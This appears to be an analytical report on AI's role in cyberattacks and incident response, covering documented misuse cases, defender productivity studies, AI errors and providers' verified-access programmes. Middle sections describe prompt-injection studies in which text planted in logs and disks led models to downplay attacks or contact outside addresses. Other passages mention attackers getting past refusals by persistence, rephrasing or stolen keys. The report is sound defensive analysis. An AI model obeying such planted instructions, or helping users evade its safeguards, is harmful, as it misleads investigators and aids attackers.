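Much AI-written attack code doesn't work. After the makers of PHP, a language behind many websites, patched two flaws on October 21, hundreds of supposed exploits appeared within days. Google thought AI had probably written them, and most were useless. But Google also counted 22 zero-days that attackers exploited in August 2026, up from an average of eight a month in 2025. AI is a plausible reason for the increase, although better detection could explain some of it.

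In its best-known case of an AI-built zero-day exploit, Google Threat Intelligence Group reported in May 2026 that criminals had planned to use the exploit against many targets at once. Nobody has named the AI model involved. The exploit bypassed the second login check in a popular open-source system administration tool, but the attacker still needed a valid username and password. The flaw was a mistaken assumption in the program's logic, a kind that conventional scanners tend to miss and language models are getting better at finding. Google worked with the software's maker to fix the flaw and may have prevented the attack.

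Google inferred the use of AI from the exploit script, which had textbook-tidy code, many explanatory comments, and a severity rating that the model had apparently made up. Google has high confidence that a model helped find the flaw and write the exploit, but doesn't believe it was Gemini. The model could have been hosted or open-weight.

### Whether banned attackers switch to open-weight models

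A common argument against strict safeguards is that attackers who lose access to a hosted model will download an open-weight one instead. The best evidence for this comes from influence operations. OpenAI's *Disrupting malicious uses of our models* (2026) describes a user linked to Chinese law enforcement who asked ChatGPT to help plan a campaign against the Japanese politician Sanae Takaichi. The model refused. About two weeks later, the user asked it to polish a status report on what was clearly the same campaign, which had gone ahead without ChatGPT's help. The wider programme ran open-weight models, including DeepSeek and Qwen, on its own machines.

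The refusal evidently didn't stop the campaign. But OpenAI doesn't establish that an open-weight model wrote the plan instead, and the hundreds of staff available could have written it themselves. The user also went back to ChatGPT for the editing, and OpenAI banned the account only later. The programme seems to have used ChatGPT and open-weight models side by side.

Other malicious users, however, have kept using hosted models. OpenAI's *PRC-linked influence operations are targeting AI debates in the US* (2026) covers two more groups, probably in China, that reached ChatGPT through VPNs even though they could have used Chinese open-weight models. OpenAI says it can't determine why. Its October 2025 report also mentions an influence operation, probably Russian, that returned to ChatGPT after an earlier disruption. The activist and the ShinyHunters affiliates responded to the cost and risk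 of hosted models by stealing access to them.

Attackers may steal keys to hosted models partly because those models work better for them than open-weight ones. GTG-50020's pursuit of an unreleased Claude model suggests that at least one group thought a stronger model was worth considerable effort. But a stolen key also saves the attacker from buying hardware and hides them behind a real customer, so someone might prefer it even if an open-weight model could do the job equally well.

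Attackers do use open-weight models, but no one has proven that bans push them to do so. Proving it would require following the same attacker from a ban to a self-hosted model, which no one did in these cases. The pattern could also change as open-weight models improve.

### What the record leaves out

A provider can see only what happens on its own models, so no company would see the whole operation if an attacker planned with ChatGPT, wrote code with Claude and ran the result through a local model. In 2025, OpenAI was noticing that more of the people it banned used several models. Providers also sometimes need outside help to spot misuse on their own services. For example, a partner's tip led to the North Korea-linked accounts described in OpenAI's *Cyber threat actors* (2025).

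Google has a wider view than the others because it also owns Mandiant, a company that investigates break-ins. According to CyberInsider, Google's September report draws on Mandiant's cases, Google's tracking of attackers and the defences on Google's platforms. Even so, investigators mostly see what an attacker left behind.

| Operation | Access to a model | How it came to light |
|---|---|---|
| North Korea-linked accounts | Ordinary accounts | A partner tipped off OpenAI |
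| Russian-speaking malware builders | Several ordinary accounts | OpenAI investigated the accounts and found the users' posts on Telegram |
| GTG-10007 and GTG-20006 | Probably ordinary accounts | Anthropic's investigators found them; it gives few details |
| GTG-50029 and ShinyHunters affiliates | Stolen keys | Anthropic's investigators found them; it gives few details |
| Fake American veteran | 73 probably stolen keys | He left his own files exposed online |
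| AI-built zero-day exploit | Unknown | Google analysed the exploit before its planned mass use |
| UNC6508 | Open model in victims' clouds | Google observed it there |
| exploit_agent | Commercial and local models | The operator left a server exposed |

Two of these cases became public because the attacker was careless with a server. The attacker in the zero-day case was careless in another way, and Google would have had much less evidence if the comments and the invented severity rating had been deleted. UNC6508 ran its model on other people's computers, where investigators had some chance of finding it. If the group had used its own hardware, investigators might have found only the attacks.

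The published record could greatly overstate the share of attackers who use hosted models if those attackers are easier to catch than the ones who run their own. Suppose that 50 attackers use hosted models and 50 run their own, and that investigators catch 20% of the first group but only 2% of the second. These rates are illustrative, because nobody knows the real ones. Investigators would find ten hosted cases and one self-hosted case, so hosted models would account for 91% of the published record but only half of the actual use.

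Published cases are also selective. Anthropic says it chose the most notable and novel ones, which it doesn't consider typical, and this makes attackers look more capable on average than they are. Providers also have reasons to write about operations they disrupted, and they can't write about those they never noticed. Google's chief analyst, John Hultquist, told reporters in September that "we can assume that all threat actors are using AI in some capacity", according to Cybersecurity Dive. That is a sensible assumption for defenders to plan around, but the published cases can't confirm it.

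### Which attackers the safeguards affect

Safeguards on hosted models probably stop some people who ask openly for malware and don't know how to divide the job into parts. No one has a good count of them, because case studies rarely cover people who give up after a refusal. Low-skilled people can still succeed, though. Trend Micro considered the fraudster it studied low-skilled, but he got what he wanted from Gemini by persisting.

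There is somewhat better evidence that restrictions keep attackers away from the strongest models. GTG-50020 failed to gain access to the one it wanted, and Anthropic found no cyber misuse of Fable or Mythos. These results are early and come from the company that built the models, but the attackers in its report did have to use weaker ones.

Safeguards on hosted models slow more capable criminals and state groups, who have to rephrase requests, assemble the pieces themselves and replace banned accounts. It is unclear how much time this adds, but it can't have been much for attackers who completed a theft within hours. Stolen keys weaken any safeguard that relies on an account's good history, because the attacker inherits that history, though checks on the content of each request still apply.

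Restricting access to hosted AI models doesn't affect attackers who run a suitable open-weight model on their own machines. It also doesn't affect those who don't need AI for the job, including anyone who already has a working password and knows where the data is.

These differences affect what a provider gains by refusing a responder. Attackers have already used mid-range models and freely available tools to explain captured exploits and map what a stolen account can reach, so refusing to help responders with these tasks probably adds little protection. There is a stronger case for restricting the use of the strongest models to write new exploits, since attackers have gone to some trouble to get those models and no one has reported them using the models for intrusions. The freight company's request for an exploit to test its patch falls between the two, because its attacker already has the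 exploit but others who want it may not.

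## How defenders use AI, and what they gain from it

How much a refusal hinders a responder depends on how much the model would have helped. Most measurements of that help come from security operations centres, the teams that watch an organisation's systems and decide which alerts need investigating. Their work overlaps with the detection and analysis stages of incident response, but an ordinary shift is much calmer than a breach. Hugging Face's own estimate, "hours instead of days", is one of the few figures from a real breach.

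### What analysts ask

The most detailed record of everyday use comes from eSentire, a company that monitors other firms' systems around the clock. *LLMs in the SOC* (Singh, Tariq and colleagues, 2025) examines 3,090 queries that 45 eSentire analysts sent to GPT-4 over ten months in 2023 and 2024. About 31% concerned commands, and the analyst typically wanted to know what a command did. Another 22% asked for help with writing, such as rephrasing an incident description, and 11% concerned code, scripts or search patterns. Analysts mostly wanted evidence explained and made the decisions themselves. One person sent about 600 of the queries, while 34 of the 45 used the model only lightly.

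Few of these requests would trigger a safeguard. The researchers discarded only 32 further queries because GPT-4 gave no meaningful answer, and some of those lacked the material the analyst meant to paste. However, eSentire barred its analysts from submitting confidential data, which probably ruled out much of what responders collect in a breach. Singh and colleagues also didn't measure whether the answers were right or saved any time.

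### Time saved on alerts

Banstola, Irving and colleagues (2026), in *It is Not Yet Another Tool*, did try to measure time. Two of the researchers worked as analysts in a university's security operations centre and built an assistant there on a small, locally run open-weight model. It searched the logs, looked up suspicious addresses, identified the device and its owner, and drafted a report. Six experienced analysts used it on 108 real tickets between April and July 2026.

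The researchers estimate that the assistant cut time per ticket by 30–50% for its three heaviest users, but they relied on the analysts' own guesses of how long the work takes by hand. One analyst closed tickets in a median of 7.6 minutes, against a guess of 15. Another took 9.9 minutes, against a guess of 10 to 20. The third took 20.6 minutes, longer than that analyst's guess of 8 minutes for a routine ticket but within the range guessed for a complex one. The measured times include interruptions, so the true saving could be larger. But the analysts chose which tickets to give the assistant, and they may have picked the ones it handled well.

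There is better evidence on how analysts used the assistant's output. They used its text in 91% of their reports but agreed with its verdict in only 67%. The assistant marked 40 alerts as uncertain, and the analysts closed 26 of them as harmless. Fifteen of those 26 had the same cause, a tunnelling service that students often run on their own devices. The analysts knew this was normal on a university network, but none of the assistant's tools could have supplied that fact.

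The study with the strongest design is *Randomized Controlled Trials for Phishing Triage Agent* (Bono, 2025), a randomised trial at Microsoft. In it, 167 professional analysts sorted emails that employees had reported as possible phishing, with or without the company's AI agent. Analysts with the agent found 6.5 times as many malicious emails per minute as those without it. That figure assumes that the agent closes every email it considers harmless and people read only the rest, an arrangement that accounted for 83% of the gain. It also assumes that the agent makes no mistakes, and it made none on the trial's 93 emails. With a less accurate agent and a higher share of malicious emails, the factor fell to 3.1.

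The trial was too small to establish Bono's conclusion that the gain in speed does not reduce protection. Analysts using the less accurate agent caught 70% of malicious emails, compared with 79% for those working alone. Adjusting for experience shrank the gap to 4 percentage points, which was not statistically significant (p = 0.497), but the result is also compatible with a true loss of about 15 points.

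A smaller experiment, *ContextBuddy* (2025), found that a single round of AI guidance on which features of an intrusion alert to examine raised accuracy from 65.4% to 86.5% and cut the time per alert from 187 to 142 seconds. With repeated guidance, accuracy stayed at 65.4%. The percentages are consistent with just 13 participants each judging four alerts per condition, so the result needs repeating.

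Vendors also report gains, but with less detail. Google (2024) says generative AI let its staff write incident summaries 51% faster. The Cloud Security Alliance, an industry body, randomly assigned 148 people to investigate alerts with or without AI and announced that AI made them faster and more accurate, according to IT Brief UK. Dropzone AI, which sells AI for such investigations, supported the project.

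### A day with 1,000 alerts

Real attacks are rare among alerts, so a model that sounds accurate can still produce mostly false alarms. Suppose a model labels 1,000 alerts, of which 10 are real attacks. Its sensitivity, the share of real attacks it flags, is 90%. Its specificity, the share of harmless alerts it leaves unflagged, is 95%. It flags 9 of the 10 real attacks and 5% of the 990 harmless alerts, which is about 50. Only about 15% of the 59 or so flagged alerts are real attacks.

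At ten minutes each, reading all 1,000 alerts would take 167 hours, or about 21 eight-hour shifts. Reading the 59 would take just under 10 hours, which is still more than one analyst can do in a normal day, and the analyst would close five or six harmless alerts for every real one. In Bono's trial, analysts confirmed 88% of the agent's correct "malicious" verdicts. At that rate, the analyst here would wrongly dismiss about one of the nine real alerts.

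The tenth attack is among 941 alerts that nobody plans to open. Spot-checking 50 of them at random would have a 5% chance of finding it. A better check is to open any unflagged alert that involves a machine, account or address from a confirmed incident.

*SIR-Bench* (2026) reports results for an actual response agent, which missed 14 of 475 real incidents (97.1% sensitivity) and wrongly flagged 85 of 319 false alarms as real (73.4% specificity). The table applies these rates, and a hypothetical higher specificity, to the same 1,000 alerts.

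| Sensitivity and specificity | Alerts flagged | Share that are real | Hours to read them |
|---|---|---|---|
| 90% and 95% | 59 | 15% | 10 |
| 90% and 99% | 19 | 48% | 3 |
| 97.1% and 73.4% (*SIR-Bench*) | 273 | 4% | 46 |

About 60% of the benchmark's cases were real incidents, compared with 1% here, so the benchmark makes false alarms look like a much smaller problem. But its false alarms may have been harder to recognise than ordinary ones, in which case the agent would do better on a live queue. *SIR-Bench* compares the agent with human analysts and says they typically catch 85–90% of real incidents, but that range comes from general operational data, not from people working the same cases.

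### Investigations and malware

After an alert proves real, responders must work out where the intruder went. In *Benchmarking and Exploring the Capabilities of LLMs for Attack Investigations*, Anand, Kantchelian and colleagues (2026) gave five models machine logs from 51 attack and harmless scenarios. On one of the two datasets, the best model found only 7 of 19 lateral movements, which are moves by an attacker from one machine to another. GPT-5 found both data thefts in that dataset without falsely reporting any others, but it flagged 12 of 145 harmless or partly harmless stretches of log as attacks, and Gemini 2.5 Pro flagged 116. These models date from 2025, so their scores are probably a poor guide to how current models perform, but tracing movement between machines is still worth testing.

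Newer models have improved quickly at reverse engineering. In the tests in *The Next Challenge for Agentic Cybersecurity* (2026), GPT-6 Astra solved between 83% and 91% of reverse-engineering tasks, depending on how the program was protected against analysis, while GPT-5.6 Sol solved between 44% and 64%. Claude Opus 5.5 cleaned up malware successfully in 76.3% of attempts, and in 82.1% after the researchers added one sentence about how they would grade the clean-up. A responder can get some of that improvement by telling the model exactly what counts as a clean machine.

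A model's average benchmark score can leave out tasks it refused. *SecRespond* (2026) simulates the work after a break-in across ten scenarios. Claude Opus 4.7 refused every attempt at one of them, a worm spreading through the NPM library of shared code, and its overall score is the average of the other nine. A team facing such a worm would get no report from the model, despite its respectable score.

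### Which gains depend on looser safeguards

Most of the measured gains come from explaining commands, looking up addresses, sorting emails and drafting reports, which safeguards rarely affect. Teams can usually get this help without verified access. The evidence on malware analysis, decoding payloads and reproducing exploits is mainly benchmarks and Hugging Face's account. None of the trials and field studies described here timed responders on such work, with or without a model.

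Looser safeguards probably help defenders little in most weeks, but a lot in the few weeks when a team is handling a serious breach. Suppose AI saves a team 150 hours a month by sorting alerts, and one breach a year needs three days of malware analysis, which a model could cut to one. Access to dual-use help would then save two days a year, while sorting alerts would save 1,800 hours. But an intruder may be active in the network during those two days, so counting hours understates their value.

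### Errors that resemble findings

Models sometimes invent indicators of compromise. In one of the 108 university tickets, the assistant named a suspicious web address that appeared neither in the alert nor in any lookup. It looked like every other address in the draft, and the analyst found the error only by asking where it had come from. A responder who searches other machines for an invented indicator will find nothing, and may take that as evidence that those machines are clean.

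The risk may be higher in the cases that matter to responders. *Beyond the Syntax* (2026) measured the share of AI-written attack detection rules that contained invented addresses or irrelevant references to known flaws. That share rose from 2.81% to 12.91% when the model's input included code demonstrating an exploit.

A simple script catches most such inventions by searching the original evidence for each indicator and rejecting any that is absent. It won't catch a real string with the wrong label. *CyberThreat-Eval* (2026) describes a model that presented a code revision's identifier as the fingerprint of a malware file. Both can be strings of 40 letters and digits, so someone has to open the source and see what the string identifies.

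The university assistant made a similar mistake about malware. An alert linked to a description of a password-stealing program as background, and the assistant reported the program as though it were on the machine, even though it had written in its draft that no matching activity had turned up there. Requiring a file or process record from the machine would have exposed the error.

A missed compromised account is harder to notice because the report doesn't mention it. The team may learn of it only when the attacker logs in again. Asking the model to look again is a weak check, since it may overlook the same entries. The freight company's responder should instead export a list of every account that has logged in to the affected machines since Friday, directly from the login records, and give each one a verdict with evidence. A person should review any account on that list that is missing from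 the model's report.

AI-written timelines can be wrong even after the system has checked its own claims. *DeepFaith* (2026) analysed 200 AI-written reports on simulated attacks and found that checking each claim against the evidence cut the rate of invented events from 21.4% to 6.1%, but the rate of errors in timing or order was still 11.2%. In practice, a common cause is that two servers use different time zones, which can make a theft appear to precede the break-in. Responders should convert all times to one zone, attach the original log line to every event in the timeline, and read the surrounding log lines for the attacker's first entry and each move to a new machine.

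People often accept such errors. *Beyond Automation* (2026) describes a penetration test, in which testers attack a system with permission, where one participant submitted an AI-assisted report that attributed stolen credentials to the wrong machine, although the attached evidence showed the right one. Bono measured this tendency by giving each analyst one malicious email that the agent had supposedly cleared. Analysts who saw the false verdict missed the email 46% of the time, compared with 17% for those working alone. False "malicious" verdicts had no clear effect, so wrongly clearing a threat seems to be the more dangerous error.

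Checking the AI's work should be quick, because telling analysts to be careful is unlikely to be enough. The *International AI Safety Report 2026* (2026) cites an experiment in which 2,784 people were less likely to correct an AI's mistakes when doing so took extra effort. At the university, analysts used the assistant on 1.4% of tickets in its first four weeks, when it reported its lookups only as text. Banstola and colleagues then had the software attach a screenshot of each source page, which the model could not fabricate, and in the last four weeks of the study, analysts used it on 47.9% of tickets. For the few conclusions that decide what to shut down, a second analyst can reach an answer before seeing the model's.

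### Instructions hidden in the evidence

Attackers write part of the evidence. A web server's log records the addresses and usernames a visitor typed, and a captured disk contains whatever files its owner left there. A model receives this material as text, along with the responder's instructions, and may follow an instruction the attacker planted in it. Security researchers call this prompt injection.

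Pandey and Bhujang (2026), in *Poisoning the Watchtower*, planted such text in invented logs and gave them to GPT-4o mini, an older small model. On average, the text succeeded 26.6% of the time with no defence and 11.8% with the strongest defence they tried. Summaries were the most vulnerable output. The manipulated summaries tended to omit or play down the attack without calling it harmless, so a filter that checks only for a false "benign" label would miss most of them.

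Planted text can also make an agent act. In *Prompt Injection Through Forensic Evidence*, Breitinger, Gruber and colleagues (2026) put notes on disks and had small local models examine the disks. One model reported that two photographs of rhinoceroses showed triceratops, because a note said so and its tools didn't let it see the pictures. In other runs, the model wrote a false error report to the investigator's machine and contacted an outside address, which could have warned a suspect. It identified the note as a possible attack before making contact, but followed it anyway. These were single demonstrations, so they give no success rate. The notes misled larger models less often, and the researchers didn't test the leading commercial ones.

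The warning signs that planted text has influenced a model are a conclusion that relies on a remark found in the evidence, an action nobody requested, or a summary that omits something an ordinary detection tool reported. Human reviewers can miss the planted text itself if, for example, it is white text on a white page, but a model still receives it among the words extracted from the document.

Responders can give the model read-only access to a copy of the evidence and no internet access. This limits what an instruction planted in the evidence can do, but the model may still reach a false conclusion, so responders should also run conventional detection rules over the same logs and account for every serious alert that the model's summary leaves out. Breitinger and colleagues also recommend planting a harmless test instruction before the model processes any real evidence. A team can do this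 with an old incident, using the same model, prompt and tools it would use in a breach, and compare the answers with and without the planted text.

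## Obtaining verified access to a hosted model

A response team will often need the provider of a hosted model to loosen its safeguards before the team can use the model to reverse-engineer malware or explain a captured exploit. Verified access is one form of what researchers call differential access, which means shaping who can use an AI system's cyber capabilities so that defenders gain more from them than attackers do. Besides keeping attackers out, the developer has to decide which defenders need these capabilities and help them get access.

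A developer can take one of three broad approaches, depending mainly on what the model can do. It can promote access to a fairly weak model by releasing it openly or paying important defenders to adopt it. With a more capable model, it can manage access by giving verified users more access than the public. If a model would give ordinary criminals the skills of a state's hackers, the developer can deny access by default and admit only a few closely vetted organisations.

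Managed access usually comes in tiers. In one sample scheme, makers of operating systems, large security vendors and software suppliers get the full model with minimal safeguards, because they can guard it well and their work protects many others. Smaller security firms and independent researchers are in the middle tier and could ask for a proof of concept for a flaw, but not for a detailed plan to attack a chosen target. Everyone else keeps the ordinary safeguards. The freight company would be in the last tier, and the response firm it hires would probably be in the middle one. Vetting delays some legitimate defenders and can widen the gap between well-resourced organisations and the rest.

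In April 2026 Anthropic came close to denying access by default when it gave its unreleased model Claude Mythos Preview to a group of mostly large technology companies and more than 40 other organisations that build or maintain critical software (Anthropic, *Project Glasswing*, 2026). OpenAI had started managing access two months earlier with a pilot based on users' identity (OpenAI, *Introducing Trusted Access for Cyber*, 2026).

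Glasswing was a poor fit for incident response because it was meant to find and fix flaws in widely used software before attackers found them. That helps a software maker more than a team with an intruder in its network. Both companies now run tiered programmes that list incident response among the permitted work.

### OpenAI's Daybreak

OpenAI's programme is now called Daybreak and has two tiers. OpenAI recommends Daybreak Blue to most security teams for work such as incident response, malware analysis and checking patches. Daybreak Red adds penetration testing, exploit development and controlled vulnerability research, and comes with models trained specially for security. The newest model dates from November 5, 2026, and OpenAI's *GPT‑6 Cyber* describes it as trained to find exploitable flaws while staying within the scope a researcher sets. Organisations with Red need further approval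 to use this model.

Individuals can apply for Blue if they are at least 18 and have an eligible paid plan. They prove their identity and set up a hardware security key, among other account protections. Only organisations can apply for Red. OpenAI may ask an organisation about its security capabilities, its planned work and the account it will use. OpenAI also considers the applicant's "ability to strengthen the broader cybersecurity ecosystem", which a freight company that defends only itself would find hard to demonstrate. Signing a contract with OpenAI doesn't guarantee approval.

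Blue reduces refusals on GPT-5.5, GPT-5.6 Sol, GPT-6 Sol and GPT-6 Luna. On GPT-6 Astra, GPT-6.1 Sol and both GPT-6.2 models, only Red reduces refusals, and Blue users face the same safeguards as the public. Most people in a hurry would pick the newest model on the list, where Blue approval gives them no benefit. OpenAI says it is working on reducing refusals for Blue users on Astra.

Until then, Blue users have to choose between a more capable model and one that refuses less often. GPT-6 Astra, for example, did much better than GPT-5.6 Sol in the reverse-engineering tests described earlier. GPT-6 Sol may be a reasonable compromise, which a team can check by running its own refusal test.

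Both tiers cover only systems, accounts, networks and data that the user owns, operates or has explicit permission to test or analyse. The freight company's responder may therefore use Daybreak to reverse-engineer the program found on the company's own server, but may not use it to probe the attacker's command-and-control server without the owner's permission, because that server belongs to somebody else (often another victim).

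### Anthropic's Cyber Verification Program

Anthropic's *Expanding the Cyber Verification Program* (2026) says that the safeguards on its generally available models "block most cyber work". On October 6, 2026, its verification programme went from one level of access to three, each of which includes the current Opus, Sonnet and Mythos models. So an approved individual can now use a successor to the model that Anthropic limited to a few dozen organisations six months earlier. Fable, Anthropic's strongest publicly available model, isn't listed.

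Defense Access is the tier for most responders. According to Anthropic, it covers incident response, malware analysis, writing detection rules, and triaging and validating vulnerabilities. The applicant needs a government photo ID and may have to take a live selfie. An organisation also gives its legal name, address and registration number, describes its security work, and attests to certain account-security controls, which become stricter on December 15, 2026.

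Red Team Access is for organisations that have permission to attack their own or their clients' systems. It allows them to develop exploits and build offensive tools. Applicants need much more evidence, such as a recognised security certificate for the company and proof of the testers' skills. Specialized Access covers testing of systems such as power grids and interbank transfers, and Anthropic reviews applications for it with the US government. Glasswing's members are moving to this tier. Anthropic says most operators of critical infrastructure need only Defense Access.

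No tier permits mass destruction of data or devices, denial-of-service attacks, physical damage, extortion, election interference, or any request with a stated malicious intent. Approval does not change the safeguards outside cybersecurity.

| Tier | Who may apply | Proof | Main work it opens | User limit | Review target |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Daybreak Blue | Individuals and organisations | Identity check; organisations also describe their security work | Incident response, malware analysis and patch validation, on some models | None stated | None stated |
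| Daybreak Red | Organisations | Separate approval with stronger verification | Penetration testing, exploit development | None stated | None stated |
| Defense Access | Individuals and organisations | Photo ID; registration details for organisations | Incident response, malware analysis, vulnerability validation | None by default | Two days |
| Red Team Access | Organisations | Evidence of an established testing team or firm | Penetration testing, exploit development | 75 | Two weeks, currently longer |
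| Specialized Access | Organisations | Authority to test critical systems, and a reason why Red Team Access is too narrow | High-risk testing of critical infrastructure | 25 | None set |

The first four of the freight company's five requests fit fairly well within Blue or Defense Access. The fifth, a working exploit to test the patch, is hard to classify. Blue includes patch validation and Defense Access includes vulnerability validation, but both providers put exploit development in a higher tier. The company is unlikely to qualify for that tier because it has no testing team of its own. It can sometimes test the patch without a new exploit by replaying the captured Friday request, unchanged, against an isolated copy of the patched server. This shows whether that particular attack still works, but a slightly different version might get through.

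Approval from either company covers only that company's models, so it doesn't help a team that relies on Google's Gemini. Anthropic's programme does extend to customers who reach Claude through Google Cloud, Microsoft Foundry or Amazon's cloud, but they must link their cloud account and then apply to Anthropic. One of the Amazon routes, Amazon Bedrock, is currently open only to organisations with an exemption from Anthropic's data retention rules. OpenAI also offers Daybreak on Bedrock, where Blue means GPT-5.6 Sol. A team whose main model comes from another provider should find out before an incident what that provider offers verified responders.

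### Turning the access on

An approved team can still get the same refusals as before, because in most products someone has to switch the access on. Daybreak's controls are off by default. According to OpenAI's onboarding instructions, a workspace owner enables Daybreak for particular users and groups, and the owner of the organisation's API account separately enables it for particular projects. A team that uses both the workspace and the API needs both steps. People who sign in to Codex, OpenAI's coding tool, with a ChatGPT account must then turn Daybreak on themselves before sending a request.

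With older models, API requests that didn't name a tier used the highest one available. Starting with GPT-6.1 Terra, they get standard safeguards. A log-analysis script that used to work could therefore start getting refusals after someone changes only the model name.

Anthropic turns access on automatically for its Pro, Max, Ultra and Team plans, including for every user on a Team plan. On an Enterprise plan, an administrator has to add the access to a custom role, since the built-in roles don't include it. In the Claude Console, where organisations manage their use of the API, an administrator assigns it to a workspace other than the default one. Customers who use Claude through a cloud provider wait about five more business days after approval for the Mythos models.

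A company can also apply from the wrong account. Anthropic treats a company's Claude account and its Console account as separate organisations, and approval for one doesn't carry over to the other. Only an owner or administrator can apply, and nobody can edit the application after submission. During a breach, the responder who needs the model may not have the authority to apply, and the person who does may be unavailable.

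Red Team Access is also limited to 75 users, including every administrator in the Console. If the organisation exceeds the limit, all of its workspaces lose Red Team Access until the number comes down. A company with 70 people enrolled that adds a dozen helpers on the first night of a breach would cut everyone off. The helpers may not qualify anyway, because only members of the team named in the application can join. Defense Access has no such limit by default.

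After switching access on, the team should test it by resending a request the model previously refused. The model would answer a harmless question about alerts with or without verified access, so that wouldn't show whether the access works.

### Refusals after approval

Approved users still meet refusals. OpenAI's *Expanding Daybreak as the Cyber Defense Window Narrows* (2026) reports how often the company's models completed advanced requests, including ones for exploit chains and ways around login checks. GPT-5.6 Sol completed 1.5% of them with standard safeguards and 2.0% with Daybreak Blue. GPT-5.6-Cyber, which comes with Daybreak Red, completed 95.0%. The older GPT-5.5-Cyber completed 57.3%, and OpenAI acknowledges that security researchers had complained of its persistent refusals.

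Blue removed the separate guardrails around GPT-5.6 Sol, so the remaining refusals must have come almost entirely from the model's own training. In *CyberDualEval*, the providers' systems accounted for nearly all refusals by Claude Opus. Both findings can be true because a filter that acts first hides what the model would have done without it. When a provider lifts the filter for a verified user, the model itself may refuse requests that the filter used to block.

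The 2.0% is a poor estimate of what a responder with Blue would experience, because all the test requests were close to attacks and OpenAI designed the test to measure how much its new model reduced refusals. Blue should help much more often with reading logs and decoding payloads, but it is unlikely to provide a working exploit to a responder who needs one.

Other evidence is less exact. OpenAI warns that some safeguards can still apply with Red, and suggests starting with a small, clearly defensive task. Anthropic tells approved users that they may meet refusals and blocks on work their tier allows while it tries to reduce false alarms. Axios' *OpenAI gives cyber defenders a less-restricted new model* (2026) reported in August that many defenders had been facing high refusal rates across the leading models, but gave no count and didn't separate verified users from the rest. No measurement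 covers a verified team working through a real incident, which is the case that matters most here.

Users can also lose access after they are verified. In a thread on OpenAI's forum, *Trusted Access for Cyber disappeared from my account*, one user describes passing verification, using Daybreak Blue for a day and then finding the account unverified. Another had the same problem although the system still listed the account as eligible. OpenAI withdraws individual approval when a user turns off the required account security or no longer has a qualifying hardware key, which may or may not explain these cases. Two posts can't show how often this happens, but they are a good reason to check access every month or so.

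A larger interruption came in June 2026, when a suspension left defenders of critical infrastructure without Mythos 5. Axios' *OpenAI rolls out more capable version of cyber model* (2026) described Anthropic on June 22 as "in limbo with the U.S. government". By June 27, the government had told Anthropic that it could restore the model to a defined set of American organisations that run or defend critical infrastructure, according to Cyber Security News (2026). Everyone else had to wait longer, whatever their own conduct or paperwork. A team that depends on one provider's strongest model needs a backup in case access is suspended.

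### Work for clients

Many organisations have no responders of their own and hire a firm when they have an incident. Both providers apply separate rules to such firms, and approval for work on a firm's own security doesn't cover work for its clients.

Anthropic distinguishes internal use (security work on an organisation's own code, products and infrastructure) from external use (work for customers). A response firm first needs approval for internal use. It then registers what Anthropic calls a managed service, in which the firm's staff use Claude and give the client only finished work they have reviewed. The client may not prompt the model or see its raw output. The firm explains how the service runs, names a security contact, and has a company officer sign off. Anthropic aims to decide in about a week. Each service needs its own approval, and a firm that serves clients without that approval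 can lose its place in the programme.

The ban on raw output could be awkward during an incident. Responders often share a screen with the client's administrators or paste results into a shared chat channel. If the results came from Claude, responders would have to review them before sharing them, which they ought to do anyway. A firm can prepare by keeping its work with the model in a channel that the client can't see.

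OpenAI's rules are harder to interpret. OpenAI allows Daybreak users to work on systems they don't own if they have explicit authorisation, which seems to cover ordinary consulting contracts. But it also restricts the access to internal use, prohibits extending it to customers, and directs firms with outside clients to its partner programme. A response firm could take the first rule as permission and later find that the second applied, so it should ask OpenAI for a written answer.

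OpenAI's *Daybreak Defense Network* describes managed services within the partner programme, in which the partner's trained staff operate the model and "customers receive the outcome". This is close to Anthropic's arrangement. Pipeline lists incident response among the services partners may provide, using Blue or Red depending on the work. Becoming a partner is slower and less certain than making an ordinary application. A firm submits a form, OpenAI contacts those it considers suitable, and they build and test the service together. According to OpenAI's *Become a Daybreak partner*, the company uses the forms to judge who might fit "a future phase" of the programme, and submitting one guarantees nothing.

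Membership doesn't show what a firm is approved to do either. When the consulting firm TrustedSec announced in October 2026 that it had joined, it said it planned to use Blue and Red in its services "where approved". An organisation choosing a response firm should therefore ask which tier the firm holds, whether its approval covers client work, and whether it has already used the model on a real case.

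### An attack found on a Saturday

Suppose the freight company's administrator notices the strange login on a Saturday morning, and neither the company nor the firm it calls has applied for anything. The firm immediately applies to Anthropic for Defense Access. Anthropic aims to decide within two days, so a decision might come on Monday, or at the end of Tuesday if only working days count. The firm can then register its managed service, which should take about another week. If Anthropic meets both targets and asks for no further information, the firm may use the model for the client nine or ten days after the administrator noticed the login.

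The company could get access sooner by submitting its own application, since work on its own systems counts as internal use. Its employees would operate the model, and the hired responders would tell them what to ask. Anthropic doesn't say whether the company could add the responders to its workspace. It tells organisations that rely on outside testers to have the testing firm apply, which suggests it would rather outsiders didn't share a client's access.

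| Arrangements in place on Saturday | Earliest use on the freight company's systems |
|---|---|
| Company has Defense Access, switched on and tested | Saturday |
| Response firm has approval for its managed service | Saturday |
| Company applies for Defense Access on Saturday | Monday or Tuesday |
| Firm has Defense Access but no approval for client work | About a week later |
| Firm has nothing and applies for both | Nine or ten days later |

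An unsuccessful applicant must wait seven days before trying again, so a mistake in the company's registration details could cause a longer delay than the review itself. Red Team Access would take two weeks even if the review met its target time. While Anthropic considers an application for a higher tier, it grants any lower tier the applicant qualifies for, so applying for Red Team Access needn't delay Defense Access.

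Helton waited a few days under the older programme, roughly in line with the present target, but that is one case and concerns an individual. OpenAI states no target for Daybreak.

Some attackers finish within hours, so a team that has to wait until Monday for access would get it too late to guide its first decisions about containment. Hugging Face got access from OpenAI too late for those decisions. Late access could still help in a long recovery, when a team may spend weeks analyzing malware and checking machines.

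It makes sense to apply for access in a quiet month. The response firm's contract can usefully require the firm to hold current approval for client work and to report any change in that approval.

### The dispute over who gets in

Some critics object to private companies making these choices at all. Schneier on Security's *Mythos and Cybersecurity* accepts that Anthropic appeared to be acting responsibly in holding Mythos back. But it objects that a company with limited staff and expertise was deciding alone which parts of the world's infrastructure to defend first, and that people who had no say would be harmed by whatever the company missed.

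Axios' *Anthropic and OpenAI are now cybersecurity's kingmakers* (2026) reported that organisations had spent two months lobbying Anthropic for Mythos Preview, and that security vendors, researchers and infrastructure operators were rushing to get the strongest models into their products and daily work. Anthropic had just widened access to more than 200 companies and governments. Axios also noted that selective access lets Anthropic and OpenAI charge for capabilities they consider too dangerous to sell openly, so they have both a financial and a safety interest in restricting access.

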